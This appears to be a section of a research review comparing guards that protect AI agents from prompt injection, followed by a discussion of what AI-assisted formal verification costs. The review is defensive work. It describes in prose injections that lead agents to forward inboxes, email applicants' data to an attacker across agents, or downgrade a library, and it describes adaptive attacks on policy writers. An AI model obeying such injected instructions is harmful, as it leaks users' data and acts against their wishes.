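An ordinary reply can contain a falsehood, just as it can contain a bad hotel recommendation. If an agent tells Alice that the government guarantees an investment fund, the action is "reply to Alice" whether or not the statement is true. Moon and Varshney therefore exclude truthfulness, deception and manipulation from what their method can guarantee.

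Code raises the same difficulty. An agent with permission to edit a login program can add a backdoor, and Tether would record the same action as it would for a legitimate repair. Sistla and colleagues estimate that 28% of the runs in one of their benchmarks and 22% in the other can't be judged without understanding the content. A company could test the new code or prove something about it, but that would need a separate specification of what the login program should do.

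A rule about actions can also fail when a person is persuaded of something false. Agenra can require a person to approve an exact call, but as Shivakumar and colleagues point out, it checks only that the approval exists, not whether the person judged well. If an agent convinces Alice that a fraudulent invoice is genuine, she will approve the payment, which will then satisfy every rule.

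## Attack experiments on rule-based guards around agents

A proof about a guard's rules doesn't show whether the rules suit the agent's work, so experiments on these guards have to count both the attacks that succeed and the tasks the agent still completes.

The table below gives both figures for two guards. CaMeL fixes an agent's plan before the agent reads any untrusted text. Progent (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) checks each tool call against a list of permissions. Narisetty and colleagues cite CaMeL's results on AgentDojo, and in June 2026 they tested Progent with a small model. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) tested both guards on longer tasks that an agent can't plan in advance. *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested adapted versions of both on command-line agents.

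| Guard | Model | Benchmark | Adaptive attack? | Attack success | User's tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | o3 | AgentDojo | No | 0% with CaMeL | 84% → 77% |
| Progent | GPT-4o | AgentDojo | No | 39.9% → 1.0% | Little change |
| Progent | Qwen2.5-7B | Part of AgentDojo | No | 25.8% → 4.2% | 45.2% → 27.1% |
| Progent | Qwen2.5-7B | Part of AgentDojo | Yes | 2.6% with Progent | 25.8% with Progent |
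| CaMeL | GPT-4o | AgentDyn | No | 37.8% → 0% | 55.5% → 0% |
| Progent | GPT-4o | AgentDyn | No | 37.8% → 1.7% | 55.5% → 5.8% |
| CaMeL-style rules | GPT-4o-mini | INFUSE | No | 46.5% → 43.0% | 54.0% → 31.5% |
| Progent-style rules | GPT-4o-mini | INFUSE | No | 46.5% → 43.0% | 54.0% → 17.0% |

With the larger models, both guards do well on AgentDojo. On AgentDyn they stop the attacks but also most of the agent's work, and on INFUSE they block some of the agent's work without clearly stopping attacks.

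### How Progent decides

A Progent policy is a list of rules about tool names and their arguments, such as "allow Slack messages to this account". Progent applies the rules that forbid calls before those that permit them, and it blocks any call that no rule covers. When it blocks a call, it normally returns an error message to the agent, which can then continue the task.

A language model writes the policy from the user's request and proposes changes as the agent works. In Shi and colleagues' example, the user asks the agent to do whatever an email titled "TODOs for the week" says:

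1. The starting policy permits only a search for that email.
2. The email asks for a summary of the user's recent messages, posted to the user's Slack account. The model proposes permission to read email, look up the account and send Slack messages.
3. The agent finds the account's name, and the model narrows the Slack permission to that account.
4. One of the recent messages contains an injection that tells the agent to forward the inbox to a stranger. If this fools the model, it proposes permission to send email.

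Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. Progent adopts a new policy P′ automatically only if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P).

The solver Z3 checks whether an update adds permissions by searching for a call that the new policy P′ allows and the old policy P doesn't, much as Amazon's Zelkova compares access policies. Step 3 narrows the policy, so it passes. Steps 2 and 4 both add permissions, so both need approval. The check doesn't distinguish the change the user wanted from the one an attacker wanted, so whoever approves the changes has to make that judgement. In the AgentDojo tests, only 6% of updates needed approval.

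### Who wrote and approved the rules

Progent's best-known result, the fall from 39.9% to 1.0%, comes from a test that approved every new permission automatically to imitate a careless user. The guarantee that permissions can't grow without approval therefore gave no protection. The result mostly shows that GPT-4o wrote good policies when the attacks were not aimed at the policy writer.

In another setting, the model wrote a policy from the user's request and never changed it, which reduced attack success to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, no attack succeeded. On another benchmark, ASB, automatic policies reduced attack success from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the remaining attacks used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of harmless ones. Rules written by hand stopped these attacks too, but Shi and colleagues doubt that even a person could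 identify the harmful tools without knowing beforehand which ones to trust.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) also points out that Progent's protection depends on its rules. Progent enforces them without exception, but people make mistakes when they write them, and a hostile tool result may lead the update mechanism to loosen them.

CaMeL's scores also depend on its policies. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, tested an agent built in their LLMbda language on AgentDojo's banking tasks. With its own checks on throughout, the agent completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policy checks off. Turning CaMeL's checks on halved the number of tasks it completed.

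Attacks on the LLMbda agent succeeded in two of 1,296 runs, or about 0.15%. The banking tasks have only 144 pairings of a user's task with an attacker's goal, and 1,296 is nine times 144, so the runs probably repeated the same pairings. Repetition measures the success rate of those attacks more precisely but doesn't test new ones. The LLMbda theorem allows untrusted text to influence an action wherever the program endorses it, so the two successes don't necessarily contradict the theorem.

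### When the user says "follow the instructions"

None of these guards works well when a user tells the agent to follow a document's instructions. In one AgentDyn request, the user says that John has sent an email about updating a code repository and asks the agent to do what it says. If an attacker can add a line to that email, the user's request covers that line too. A CaMeL planner can't write the program without reading the email, Progent has to add permissions based on the email, and an LLMbda program has to endorse the email.

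Each system can pass the decision to a person, but people who approve requests all day may stop reading them. Narisetty and colleagues call this the deepest open problem for guards of this kind.

Li and colleagues found that only six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan in response to what it reads. For a task such as "pay this bill", the agent can work out at the start that it must read a file and send money. Li and colleagues wrote AgentDyn's 60 tasks so that all of them require such a change. These tasks take 7.1 steps on average, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo, and the agent has about 33 tools instead of 20.

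Every AgentDyn task also contains a helpful instruction from a third party. In one task, a shop's checkout page displays a notice that the shop has emailed a one-time password, which the agent must fetch before it can pay. In another task, a friend writes that her light bulb isn't working, asks the user to buy a replacement, and supplies the name and password of her shopping account to pay for it. The benchmark treats the request as genuine, though a careful person might well think it was a fraud.

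CaMeL completed no tasks with any of the four models in the main comparison. Progent did a little better, completing 16% of tasks under attack with Gemini 2.5 Pro, compared with 57% for the same model without a guard. Li and colleagues found that Progent's policy writer made mistakes when there were many tools. These mistakes accumulated, and by the later steps of a long task Progent was blocking almost every useful tool.

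Li and colleagues chose only tasks that can't be completed with a fixed plan, so CaMeL's score of zero shows that it can't do this kind of task but doesn't measure how often users ask for one. They also told the agents to finish every task without asking for confirmation, because an agent that stopped to ask would fail the test. The results are therefore weak evidence about agents whose users are present to approve an extra step. FIDES, which chooses one step at a time, might cope better with these tasks, but Li and colleagues didn't test it.

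### Rules for a command line

INFUSE, a benchmark published in October 2026, has 40 tasks, such as repairing a program or installing software, and 56 attacks hidden in files, file names and program output. The agent has one tool, which runs Bash commands.

Nguyen and colleagues tested their two adapted guards on 200 combinations of task and attack with each of five models. Nine of the ten resulting attack success rates were within the margin of error of the rate without a guard. The tenth, for Claude Sonnet 4.6 with the Progent-style rules, rose from 6.5% to 27.1%. A guard that only blocks commands shouldn't make an agent easier to hijack, so something else probably differed between the runs. One possible cause is the spending limit, which cut short many of this model's runs in the main experiment. The Progent-style rules also reduced the number of completed tasks by 64% to 75% on three of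 the four models with task completion data.

These results look like a refutation of the earlier ones, but the experiment differs from them in at least four ways.

Nguyen and colleagues tested their own adaptations of the guards and limit their conclusions to these versions. Their version of CaMeL omits the interpreter and the quarantined model. It derives a policy from the user's request and uses it to block some commands, but the main model still reads everything and chooses each command as it goes.

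Rules about tools also work poorly for shell commands. Progent is designed for calls that have a name and separate arguments, such as "send this message to this account". The researchers had to break each Bash command into simple operations and check those against a list. A rule that permits scripts, or any action this general, restricts very little, but forbidding scripts prevents much ordinary programming.

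Many of the attacks asked for actions the agent might have had permission to take anyway. One told it to edit a project's list of required software so that the project would use an old library version with known vulnerabilities. If the user has asked the agent to repair that list, the rules must let it edit the file. None of the 20 attacks in this part of the experiment tried to steal data, the harm CaMeL's labels are best suited to prevent.

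Finally, the two benchmarks define success differently. AgentDojo counts an attack as successful only if the attacker's goal is achieved. In the tests of the adapted guards, a language model read the record of each run and decided whether the injection had influenced the agent, with instructions to count even partial compliance. If an agent tries to add an attacker's key to a server and the guard blocks the command, AgentDojo would record a failed attack, but INFUSE's judge could reasonably record a success. The judge also undercounted compliance in a sample that people labelled too, missing 24 of the 60 runs in which they thought the agent had complied.

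INFUSE is still a useful warning to anyone who plans to add such rules to an agent with a command line. A developer who copies the idea of CaMeL or Progent without its supporting structure may get the inconvenience but little of the protection. Guards that restrict what a command does, as Tether tries to, may suit such agents better.

The software around a model affects whether attacks succeed, even without a guard. When Nguyen and colleagues replayed 456 successful attacks in Claude Code and Codex CLI, two widely used coding agents, only 102 worked again, although the model, task and attack were the same.

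In INFUSE, other defences did much better than the adapted guards. MetaSecAlign's training reduced attack success by 55% in a small model and 74% in a larger one. Repeated warnings to ignore outside instructions reduced attack success from 58.2% to 14.3% on a set of especially vulnerable tasks. But the attacks did not adapt to the defences, and both MetaSecAlign and simple prompting defences had failed against Nasr and colleagues' adaptive search.

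### Injections that pass between agents

Even the original CaMeL can fail when several agents work together. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, built a system in which a coordinator gives jobs to a database agent and a notification agent. All three ran CaMeL. The user asked for a summary of some job applicants' details to go to Julie on Slack, and the coordinator's planner wrote a program much like this:

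```
info    = database_agent("Retrieve the applicants' details.")
summary = ask_quarantined_model("Summarize this.", info)
notification_agent("Send this summary to Julie on Slack: " + summary)
```

The database contained an instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address. Neither the coordinator's planner nor the database agent's planner read it. But the last line of the program pasted the summary, which included the instruction, into a message that the notification agent treated as its own user's request. The notification agent's planner read the instruction and added a step that emailed the details to the attacker.

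The same mistake causes SQL injection, and the fix resembles a parameterized query. In multi-CaMeL, the researchers' new version, one agent sends another an instruction and a separate set of values. The receiving planner reads only the instruction, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. Multi-CaMeL has the same flaw with skipped branches as CaMeL, so it can still miss some dependencies.

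To measure the problem, Peters-Gill and colleagues divided AgentDojo's tools among several agents and ran 949 attacked tasks on each of five models. On average, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent, and never with multi-CaMeL. With GPT-4.1, the figures were 36.1%, 0.5% and zero. Every attack that got past the separate CaMeL agents crossed from one agent to another in this way. An attacker who designed injections to cross between agents would probably succeed more than 0.2% of the time.

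These tests ran CaMeL with its policies off, so they measured only whether an attacker could change the plan, not whether the attacker could corrupt the values in a permitted call.

The researchers measured usefulness on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks for teams of agents. Giving each agent CaMeL reduced the share of completed tasks by 21.6 percentage points on average, and multi-CaMeL reduced it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the reductions were 13.4 and 0.85 points. Better models may lose less usefulness under this protection, perhaps because they write programs that anticipate more of what could happen. Most of the failures still came from committing to a plan before seeing the data.

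AgentDojo is also dated as a test of strong models. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without CaMeL, so the benchmark couldn't show any benefit from adding the guard. Claude Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 ordinary tasks when no attack was present. Peters-Gill and colleagues suspect that the model associated AgentDojo's settings with attacks.

### The June 2026 adaptive test

Narisetty and colleagues' test is the only one in the table in which the attacker adapted to the guard. They used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, both as the agent and as Progent's policy writer, and ran it on eight tasks from each of AgentDojo's banking, Slack and office settings. Their attack described the harmful action as a routine step the user had already authorised, hoping the policy writer would add the permission.

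The attack succeeded 2.6% of the time on average, less often than the ordinary attack's 4.2%. The average conceals opposite results. Three repetitions gave 120 attacked runs on Slack and 216 on banking:

| Setting | Ordinary attack, no guard | Ordinary attack, Progent | Adaptive attack, Progent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Slack | 70 of 120 | 13 of 120 | 5 of 120 |
| Banking | 41 of 216 | 4 of 216 | 8 of 216 |

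In the office setting, no attack worked even without Progent, because the model answered the user's questions and ignored the injections. So the comparison depends only on the other two settings, where the numbers are small.

The researchers suggest that the rate was lower on Slack because the softer wording may have persuaded the agent less often. They did not run the adaptive attack on an agent without Progent, so it is unclear how much of the low rate is due to the guard and how much to a weak attack. They also tried only one template, whereas Nasr and colleagues' search kept revising its text. Progent's developers had run their own adaptive attacks with GPT-4o and, according to Narisetty and colleagues, found success rates between 0.5% and 4.2%.

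Progent's cost was clearer than its resistance to adaptive attacks. The share of completed tasks fell by more than half on Slack and by about half in the office setting, though it didn't change in banking under the ordinary attack. The agent also needed about 15 times as many calls to a language model. (Narisetty and colleagues work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools on the same principle as Progent.)

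### What an adequate adaptive test would need

Narisetty and colleagues' protocol includes much more than they carried out. In the full protocol, the attacker knows the policy and optimises the text against the guard over many attempts. The attacker also tries to give untrusted text a trusted label, trick the person who approves exceptions, and extract information through side channels. Testers record how often the attacks succeed, how many tasks the agent completes, and how often it asks for approval.

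The experiments suggest further requirements. Testers should run each adaptive attack on the agent with and without the guard, and discard attacks that fail without it. They should test the original guard with its policies turned on, and the people or models that write those policies shouldn't have access to the attacks. Code should check the mailbox, account or files afterwards, so that a blocked attempt doesn't count as a successful attack. The tasks should include requests like the one about John's email, about as often as real users make them.

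Above all, the attacker should try to cause harm using only the permissions the guard has granted. For example, an agent allowed to pay a bill could pay the wrong amount, and one allowed to post a summary could post a false one. The Progent paper puts these attacks out of scope, and Narisetty and colleagues plan to test them next. To do this against CaMeL, the attacker would have to corrupt the values that the quarantined model returns.

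## What testing and proof cost, and how AI has changed it

Designing adaptive attacks takes skilled work, but proofs have usually taken far more, which for decades made them impractical for most software. AI has now sharply reduced the work a proof takes, at least for programs of a few thousand lines.

### The price of a first proof

Figures for the effort behind seL4 vary, mostly because they count different things. Trustworthy Systems puts the whole project at about 25 person-years, including early models that it later discarded. *SafeJIT* (Ebner, 2026) puts the proof and its tools at about 20 person-years, with about 11 of those spent on the proof of seL4 itself. The kernel had 8,700 lines of C, so even the lowest figure works out to about three lines verified per person per working day. Donaldson puts the refinement proof at about 165,000 lines, or 19 for every line of C.

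Concurrent code, whose parts run at the same time, can be even slower to prove correct. *Rely-guarantee Reasoning about Concurrent Memory Management* (2023) reports that a proof about the memory manager of Zephyr, an operating system for small devices, took 14 person-months. The manager has about 400 lines of C, so the proof covered about 29 lines per person-month.

*Fast, Secure, Adaptable* (2025) puts the cost of verifying seL4 at $350 a line. That is less than the $1,000 a line that Trustworthy Systems cites as a rule of thumb for strict certification by conventional means. But most software never goes through such certification, so its makers compare the cost of a proof with that of ordinary testing.

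Checking a design takes much less effort than proving the code. One Amazon engineer learned TLA+ and wrote a useful specification in two weeks. But *A Systematic Literature Review on a Decade of Industrial TLA+ Practice* (2024) concludes that a steep learning curve and the difficulty of deciding what a model should leave out still hinder adoption.

### The price of testing

Machine time for fuzzing costs little. Csmith's million-program run on GCC and LLVM used a little over two years of one core's time, which would cost about $1,000 at five cents an hour for a rented core.

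Most of the expense of testing is the labor of building the generator, working out which failures share a cause, and persuading developers to fix them. Nobody has compared those hours with the hours needed for a proof of the same program, so there is no fair figure for the cost per bug.

Testing is also less likely to waste effort. A team can stop fuzzing after a week and keep every bug it has found. Donaldson warns that engineers using a proof assistant never know how close they are to finishing. A minor lemma may need an extra assumption, which the engineer then has to carry through every theorem that depends on the lemma.

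### Keeping a proof valid

A proof that one version of a program is correct doesn't establish that later versions are. Donaldson notes that when seL4's developers added a new kind of capability for replying to messages, proving the kernel correct again took about a person-year.

Harmless edits can break proofs that rely on automatic solvers. A solver searches for a proof by rules of thumb, and renaming a variable can change the search. Donaldson cites reports from Amazon that code written in Dafny stopped verifying after small, seemingly unrelated edits. On a verified authorization engine, the problem worsened as the code grew, until it delayed releases.

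Good design can reduce this work. Keel stores its rules for rewriting formulas in a table, separate from the code that applies them. To add 13 rules, Cai and colleagues wrote 633 lines of Lean, mostly to define each rule and prove it sound, and didn't have to change any of the C functions. Changing the functions would be harder, because the proof that connects them to the specification is 52,398 lines long. Another 12,863 lines prove the limits on time and memory.

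### What practitioners say

For Brugger, Denis and Müller (2025), in *Toward Practical Deductive Verification*, the question was why so few engineers prove their programs correct. They contacted 56 people with experience of doing so, interviewed 30 (54%), and analysed 29 of the interviews. These are some of the difficulties that came up:

| Difficulty | Interviewees who raised it (of 29) |
|---|---|
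| The work needs a lot of expertise | 19 |
| Automatic tools are slow | 16 |
| Results are hard to explain to non-experts | 15 |
| Tools are immature | 13 |
| Tools have a steep learning curve | 12 |
| Proofs are hard to maintain | 12 |
| The benefit may not justify the cost | 10 |

These counts come from open-ended interviews, so someone who never mentioned maintenance may still consider it a serious problem. The sample leaves out engineers who looked at formal methods and decided against them. Of the 30 people interviewed, 27 were students or senior researchers and 17 had helped develop the tools they used, though most of the interviews covered industrial projects.

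The list is consistent with other evidence. *Applying Formal Methods Tools to an Electronic Warfare Codebase (Experience report)* (2026) cites surveys of experts in which the main barriers were a lack of training, poorly maintained academic tools, poor fit with industrial work, and the learning curve.

### Two systems proved with AI

Language models suit this work because proofs are hard to find but easy to check. If a model writes a wrong proof, Lean rejects it, so the mistake only wastes time. Cai and colleagues used AI tools from Anthropic and Google to develop Keel's proofs, but chose the design and theorems themselves. Two larger projects published their costs in detail.

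*Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (Kaashoek and Zeldovich, 2026) describes a proof about xv6, a small Unix-like kernel that universities use for teaching. The proof concerns the compiled machine code running on several processor cores that can lose power at any moment. One consequence is that if a user types `echo hello world`, the system can print only "hello world" or one of a few listed errors. Claude Code wrote the proofs, while Kaashoek and Zeldovich planned the work and designed the main abstractions.

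Ebner directed AI agents that wrote the code and the proofs for SafeJIT, a small JavaScript engine with a JIT compiler. Like eBPF's JIT compiler, SafeJIT's compiler translates programs that an attacker may have written. The theorem is that no input can crash the engine. It covers the engine's own machine code and any code the engine generates while running.

The table compares these projects with two earlier ones. It leaves out generated files and, where the sources count them separately, reusable frameworks.

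| System | Lines of code | Lines of proof per line of code | People's time | Lines of code per person-month |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| seL4 | 8,700 | 19 | 11 person-years | 66 |
| Zephyr memory manager | 400 | 45 | 14 person-months | 29 |
| xv6 | 6,657 | 109 | At most 7 person-months | About 1,000 |
| SafeJIT | 6,476 | 64 | About 1 person-month | About 6,500 |

The time for xv6 assumes both researchers worked on it throughout the project's 102 days, and includes building a new framework. The proofs for xv6 and SafeJIT are longer per line of code, partly because they deal with individual machine instructions. Length matters less when a person doesn't have to write or read the proof.

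The theorems also differ. seL4's requires correct behaviour, whereas SafeJIT's would still hold if the engine got every sum wrong. The xv6 proof doesn't show that one program can't leak data to another, but seL4's security proofs show this for some versions of seL4. So some of the saving comes from proving less, but that can hardly explain a difference of 15 times or more.

### What the tokens would cost

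Kaashoek and Zeldovich paid less than $3,000 for subscriptions to Claude, plus the cost of rented computers. A subscription can hide much of the real expense. *EconCSLib* (2026), a project that translates economics papers into Lean, used tokens worth about $16,400 at OpenAI's list prices, but a subscription at $200 a month covered them. Those prices work out at $5 per million tokens of new input, $0.50 per million of cached input (text the service has already processed), and $30 per million of output. At the same prices, the xv6 project's tokens would have cost

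2,500 × $5 + 171,800 × $0.50 + 235 × $30 ≈ $105,000,

where the quantities are in millions of tokens. Most of this is for cached input, because an agent rereads its earlier work at every step.

The researchers' seven person-months would add about $145,000, at the roughly $250,000 per person-year implied by seL4's $350 a line. The total is a little under $40 a line for xv6, about a ninth of the seL4 figure. The same calculation for SafeJIT gives about $4 a line. These estimates are rough because they apply one company's prices to another company's models and ignore inflation and the rented computers. They still suggest that a proof about a small kernel now costs hundreds of thousands of dollars instead of millions.

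Maintaining a proof also takes less work now. The xv6 proof refers to exact addresses in the compiled kernel, so almost any edit to the source code breaks parts of it. Kaashoek and Zeldovich updated the kernel 26 times during the project. For the 25 updates they could measure, the median was 35 minutes of the agent's time and two prompts from a person. The slowest took 12.2 hours, after a change that added a check to the code and altered the specification. That is still far less than the person-year seL4's developers spent on one change, but most of the xv6 changes were smaller than that one, so the comparison overstates AI's advantage.

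AI may help less with model checking. Donaldson points out that even a clever AI can't reduce the number of states in a design, though it can help engineers repair their models and adjust the solver's settings.

### Bugs that testing had missed

The xv6 proof exposed 11 bugs in the kernel, some of which could crash it. In one, xv6 counted the links to each file without checking for overflow. A program that created enough links could make the count negative, and the kernel would then halt when somebody deleted a link.

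Another bug shows how a test environment can hide a mistake. A RISC-V processor relies on the kernel to record which pages of memory a program has used, unless the kernel switches on automatic recording. xv6 never switched it on and couldn't handle the processor's requests to record page use. Its developers had tested it only on QEMU, a program that imitates the hardware. QEMU switches on automatic recording by itself, so more tests on it would not have revealed the bug.

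AI can also find bugs by reading code, as it did in BCF's old checker. Keel's specification helped because it gave the AI tools a description of what the code should do. AI has also reduced the work of testing. It helped Cai and colleagues write their fuzzer, and agents wrote 12,065 lines of assembly code to test the xv6 project's hardware model.

These cases don't measure how much testing has missed in the most heavily tested software. The xv6 kernel, for instance, is meant for teaching. A count of the bugs testing missed in a browser or compiler that others have fuzzed for years would be better evidence.

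### Will cheap proofs make verified interfaces normal?

*AI with Authority, from Application to Silicon* (2026) argues that verification is essential to productivity when AI writes code. AI can write code much faster than people can review it, so a proof checker makes the output usable. The paper also gives the main objection to its own optimism, which is that AI has made proofs easier to produce but not, by itself, easier to trust.

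The xv6 figures allow a rough test of that reply. Nobody has to read the 1.6 million lines of proof, but an expert still has to read the theorem and the definitions it depends on. For the theorem about the console, Kaashoek and Zeldovich count 4,627 lines of these, excluding the official description of the processor, which is about 70% of the length of the kernel. About 3,000 of the lines describe memory and devices, and a proof about another kernel could reuse them. The other 1,600 or so specify what the console may show.

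Mistakes in those definitions are common enough to matter. The xv6 team compared its model with QEMU and real processors in 77 tests and found 35 discrepancies. Many were harmless, but in the model, the disk carried out requests in order, while QEMU's disk may reorder them. The team corrected the model and then had to revise the proof of the disk driver.

Ebner describes a worse case, involving a RISC-V processor, which can keep running old instructions after a program has replaced them unless the program requests that its instruction cache be cleared. SafeJIT made the request but never checked whether it had succeeded. The agent that wrote the proofs had also written the model of the system, which left out this cache, so the proof succeeded. An agent based on a different language model found this gap and another one within minutes. Once Ebner's agents corrected the system model, the proof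 failed at the faulty code. Review by AI can therefore also reduce the work needed to trust a proof, but somebody had to think of asking for it.

Many specifications get no such review. *EconCSLib* has 986,391 lines of Lean that the checker accepts, but people have not finished checking that its theorems match the original papers. Moon and Varshney used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens for each of their PocketFlow runs. Even at $30 per million tokens, the most expensive run would have cost about $100. One of those runs produced the rule about an empty list, which restricted nothing, and cheaper proofs would not have fixed that.

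Specifications were already a problem before AI wrote proofs. In interviews by Brugger and colleagues, 11 of 29 people said that verification is feasible only when the requirements are well defined, or that it is of little use when they aren't. This favours verifying guards rather than whole agents, because agents' tasks are harder to define.

Expertise also remains scarce, although AI has changed what experts do. Ebner wrote about 180 prompts, 68 of which were some form of "please continue". But on the fifth day, Ebner noticed that the agent was using an unsuitable proof method, and the agent had to convert about 28,000 lines. Kaashoek and Zeldovich wrote about 160,000 words of prompts. Donaldson, who learned Lean with AI's help, expects many more people to know enough to be effective, but fewer to have deep expertise, which reviewers of specifications need.

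Old code is a further obstacle, and size is the main reason. At $40 a line, verifying the 26 million lines of Linux would cost about a billion dollars, and the price per line would probably rise. *QED at Large* (2020) reports that effort on seL4 grew in proportion to the length of the proof, and that the length of a proof grew with the square of the size of the property. If a specification of size s costs c·s² to prove, splitting it into k equal and independent parts reduces the cost to

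k × c(s/k)² = c·s²/k.

If proof effort grows with the square of a system's size, proving ten equal, independent parts would take a tenth of the effort of proving the whole. Real parts interact, so the saving would be smaller, and nobody knows whether the square law holds for proofs written by AI. But the law explains why engineers who want proofs prefer small components with simple interfaces.

The xv6 project shows that old code doesn't always need to be replaced before it can be verified. Its developers had not designed the kernel for verification, but the researchers changed little beyond fixing bugs and removing a debugging feature that read the list of running programs without the proper locks. Production software is harder to verify. SafeJIT leaves out much of JavaScript, as well as the advanced optimisations where, according to Ebner, most bugs in commercial JIT compilers occur.

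A verified guard can avoid much of this work if it is a drop-in replacement for an unverified one. Keel reads the same certificates as the old checker and connects to the kernel at the same points, so kernel developers could switch to it without rewriting the rest of eBPF.
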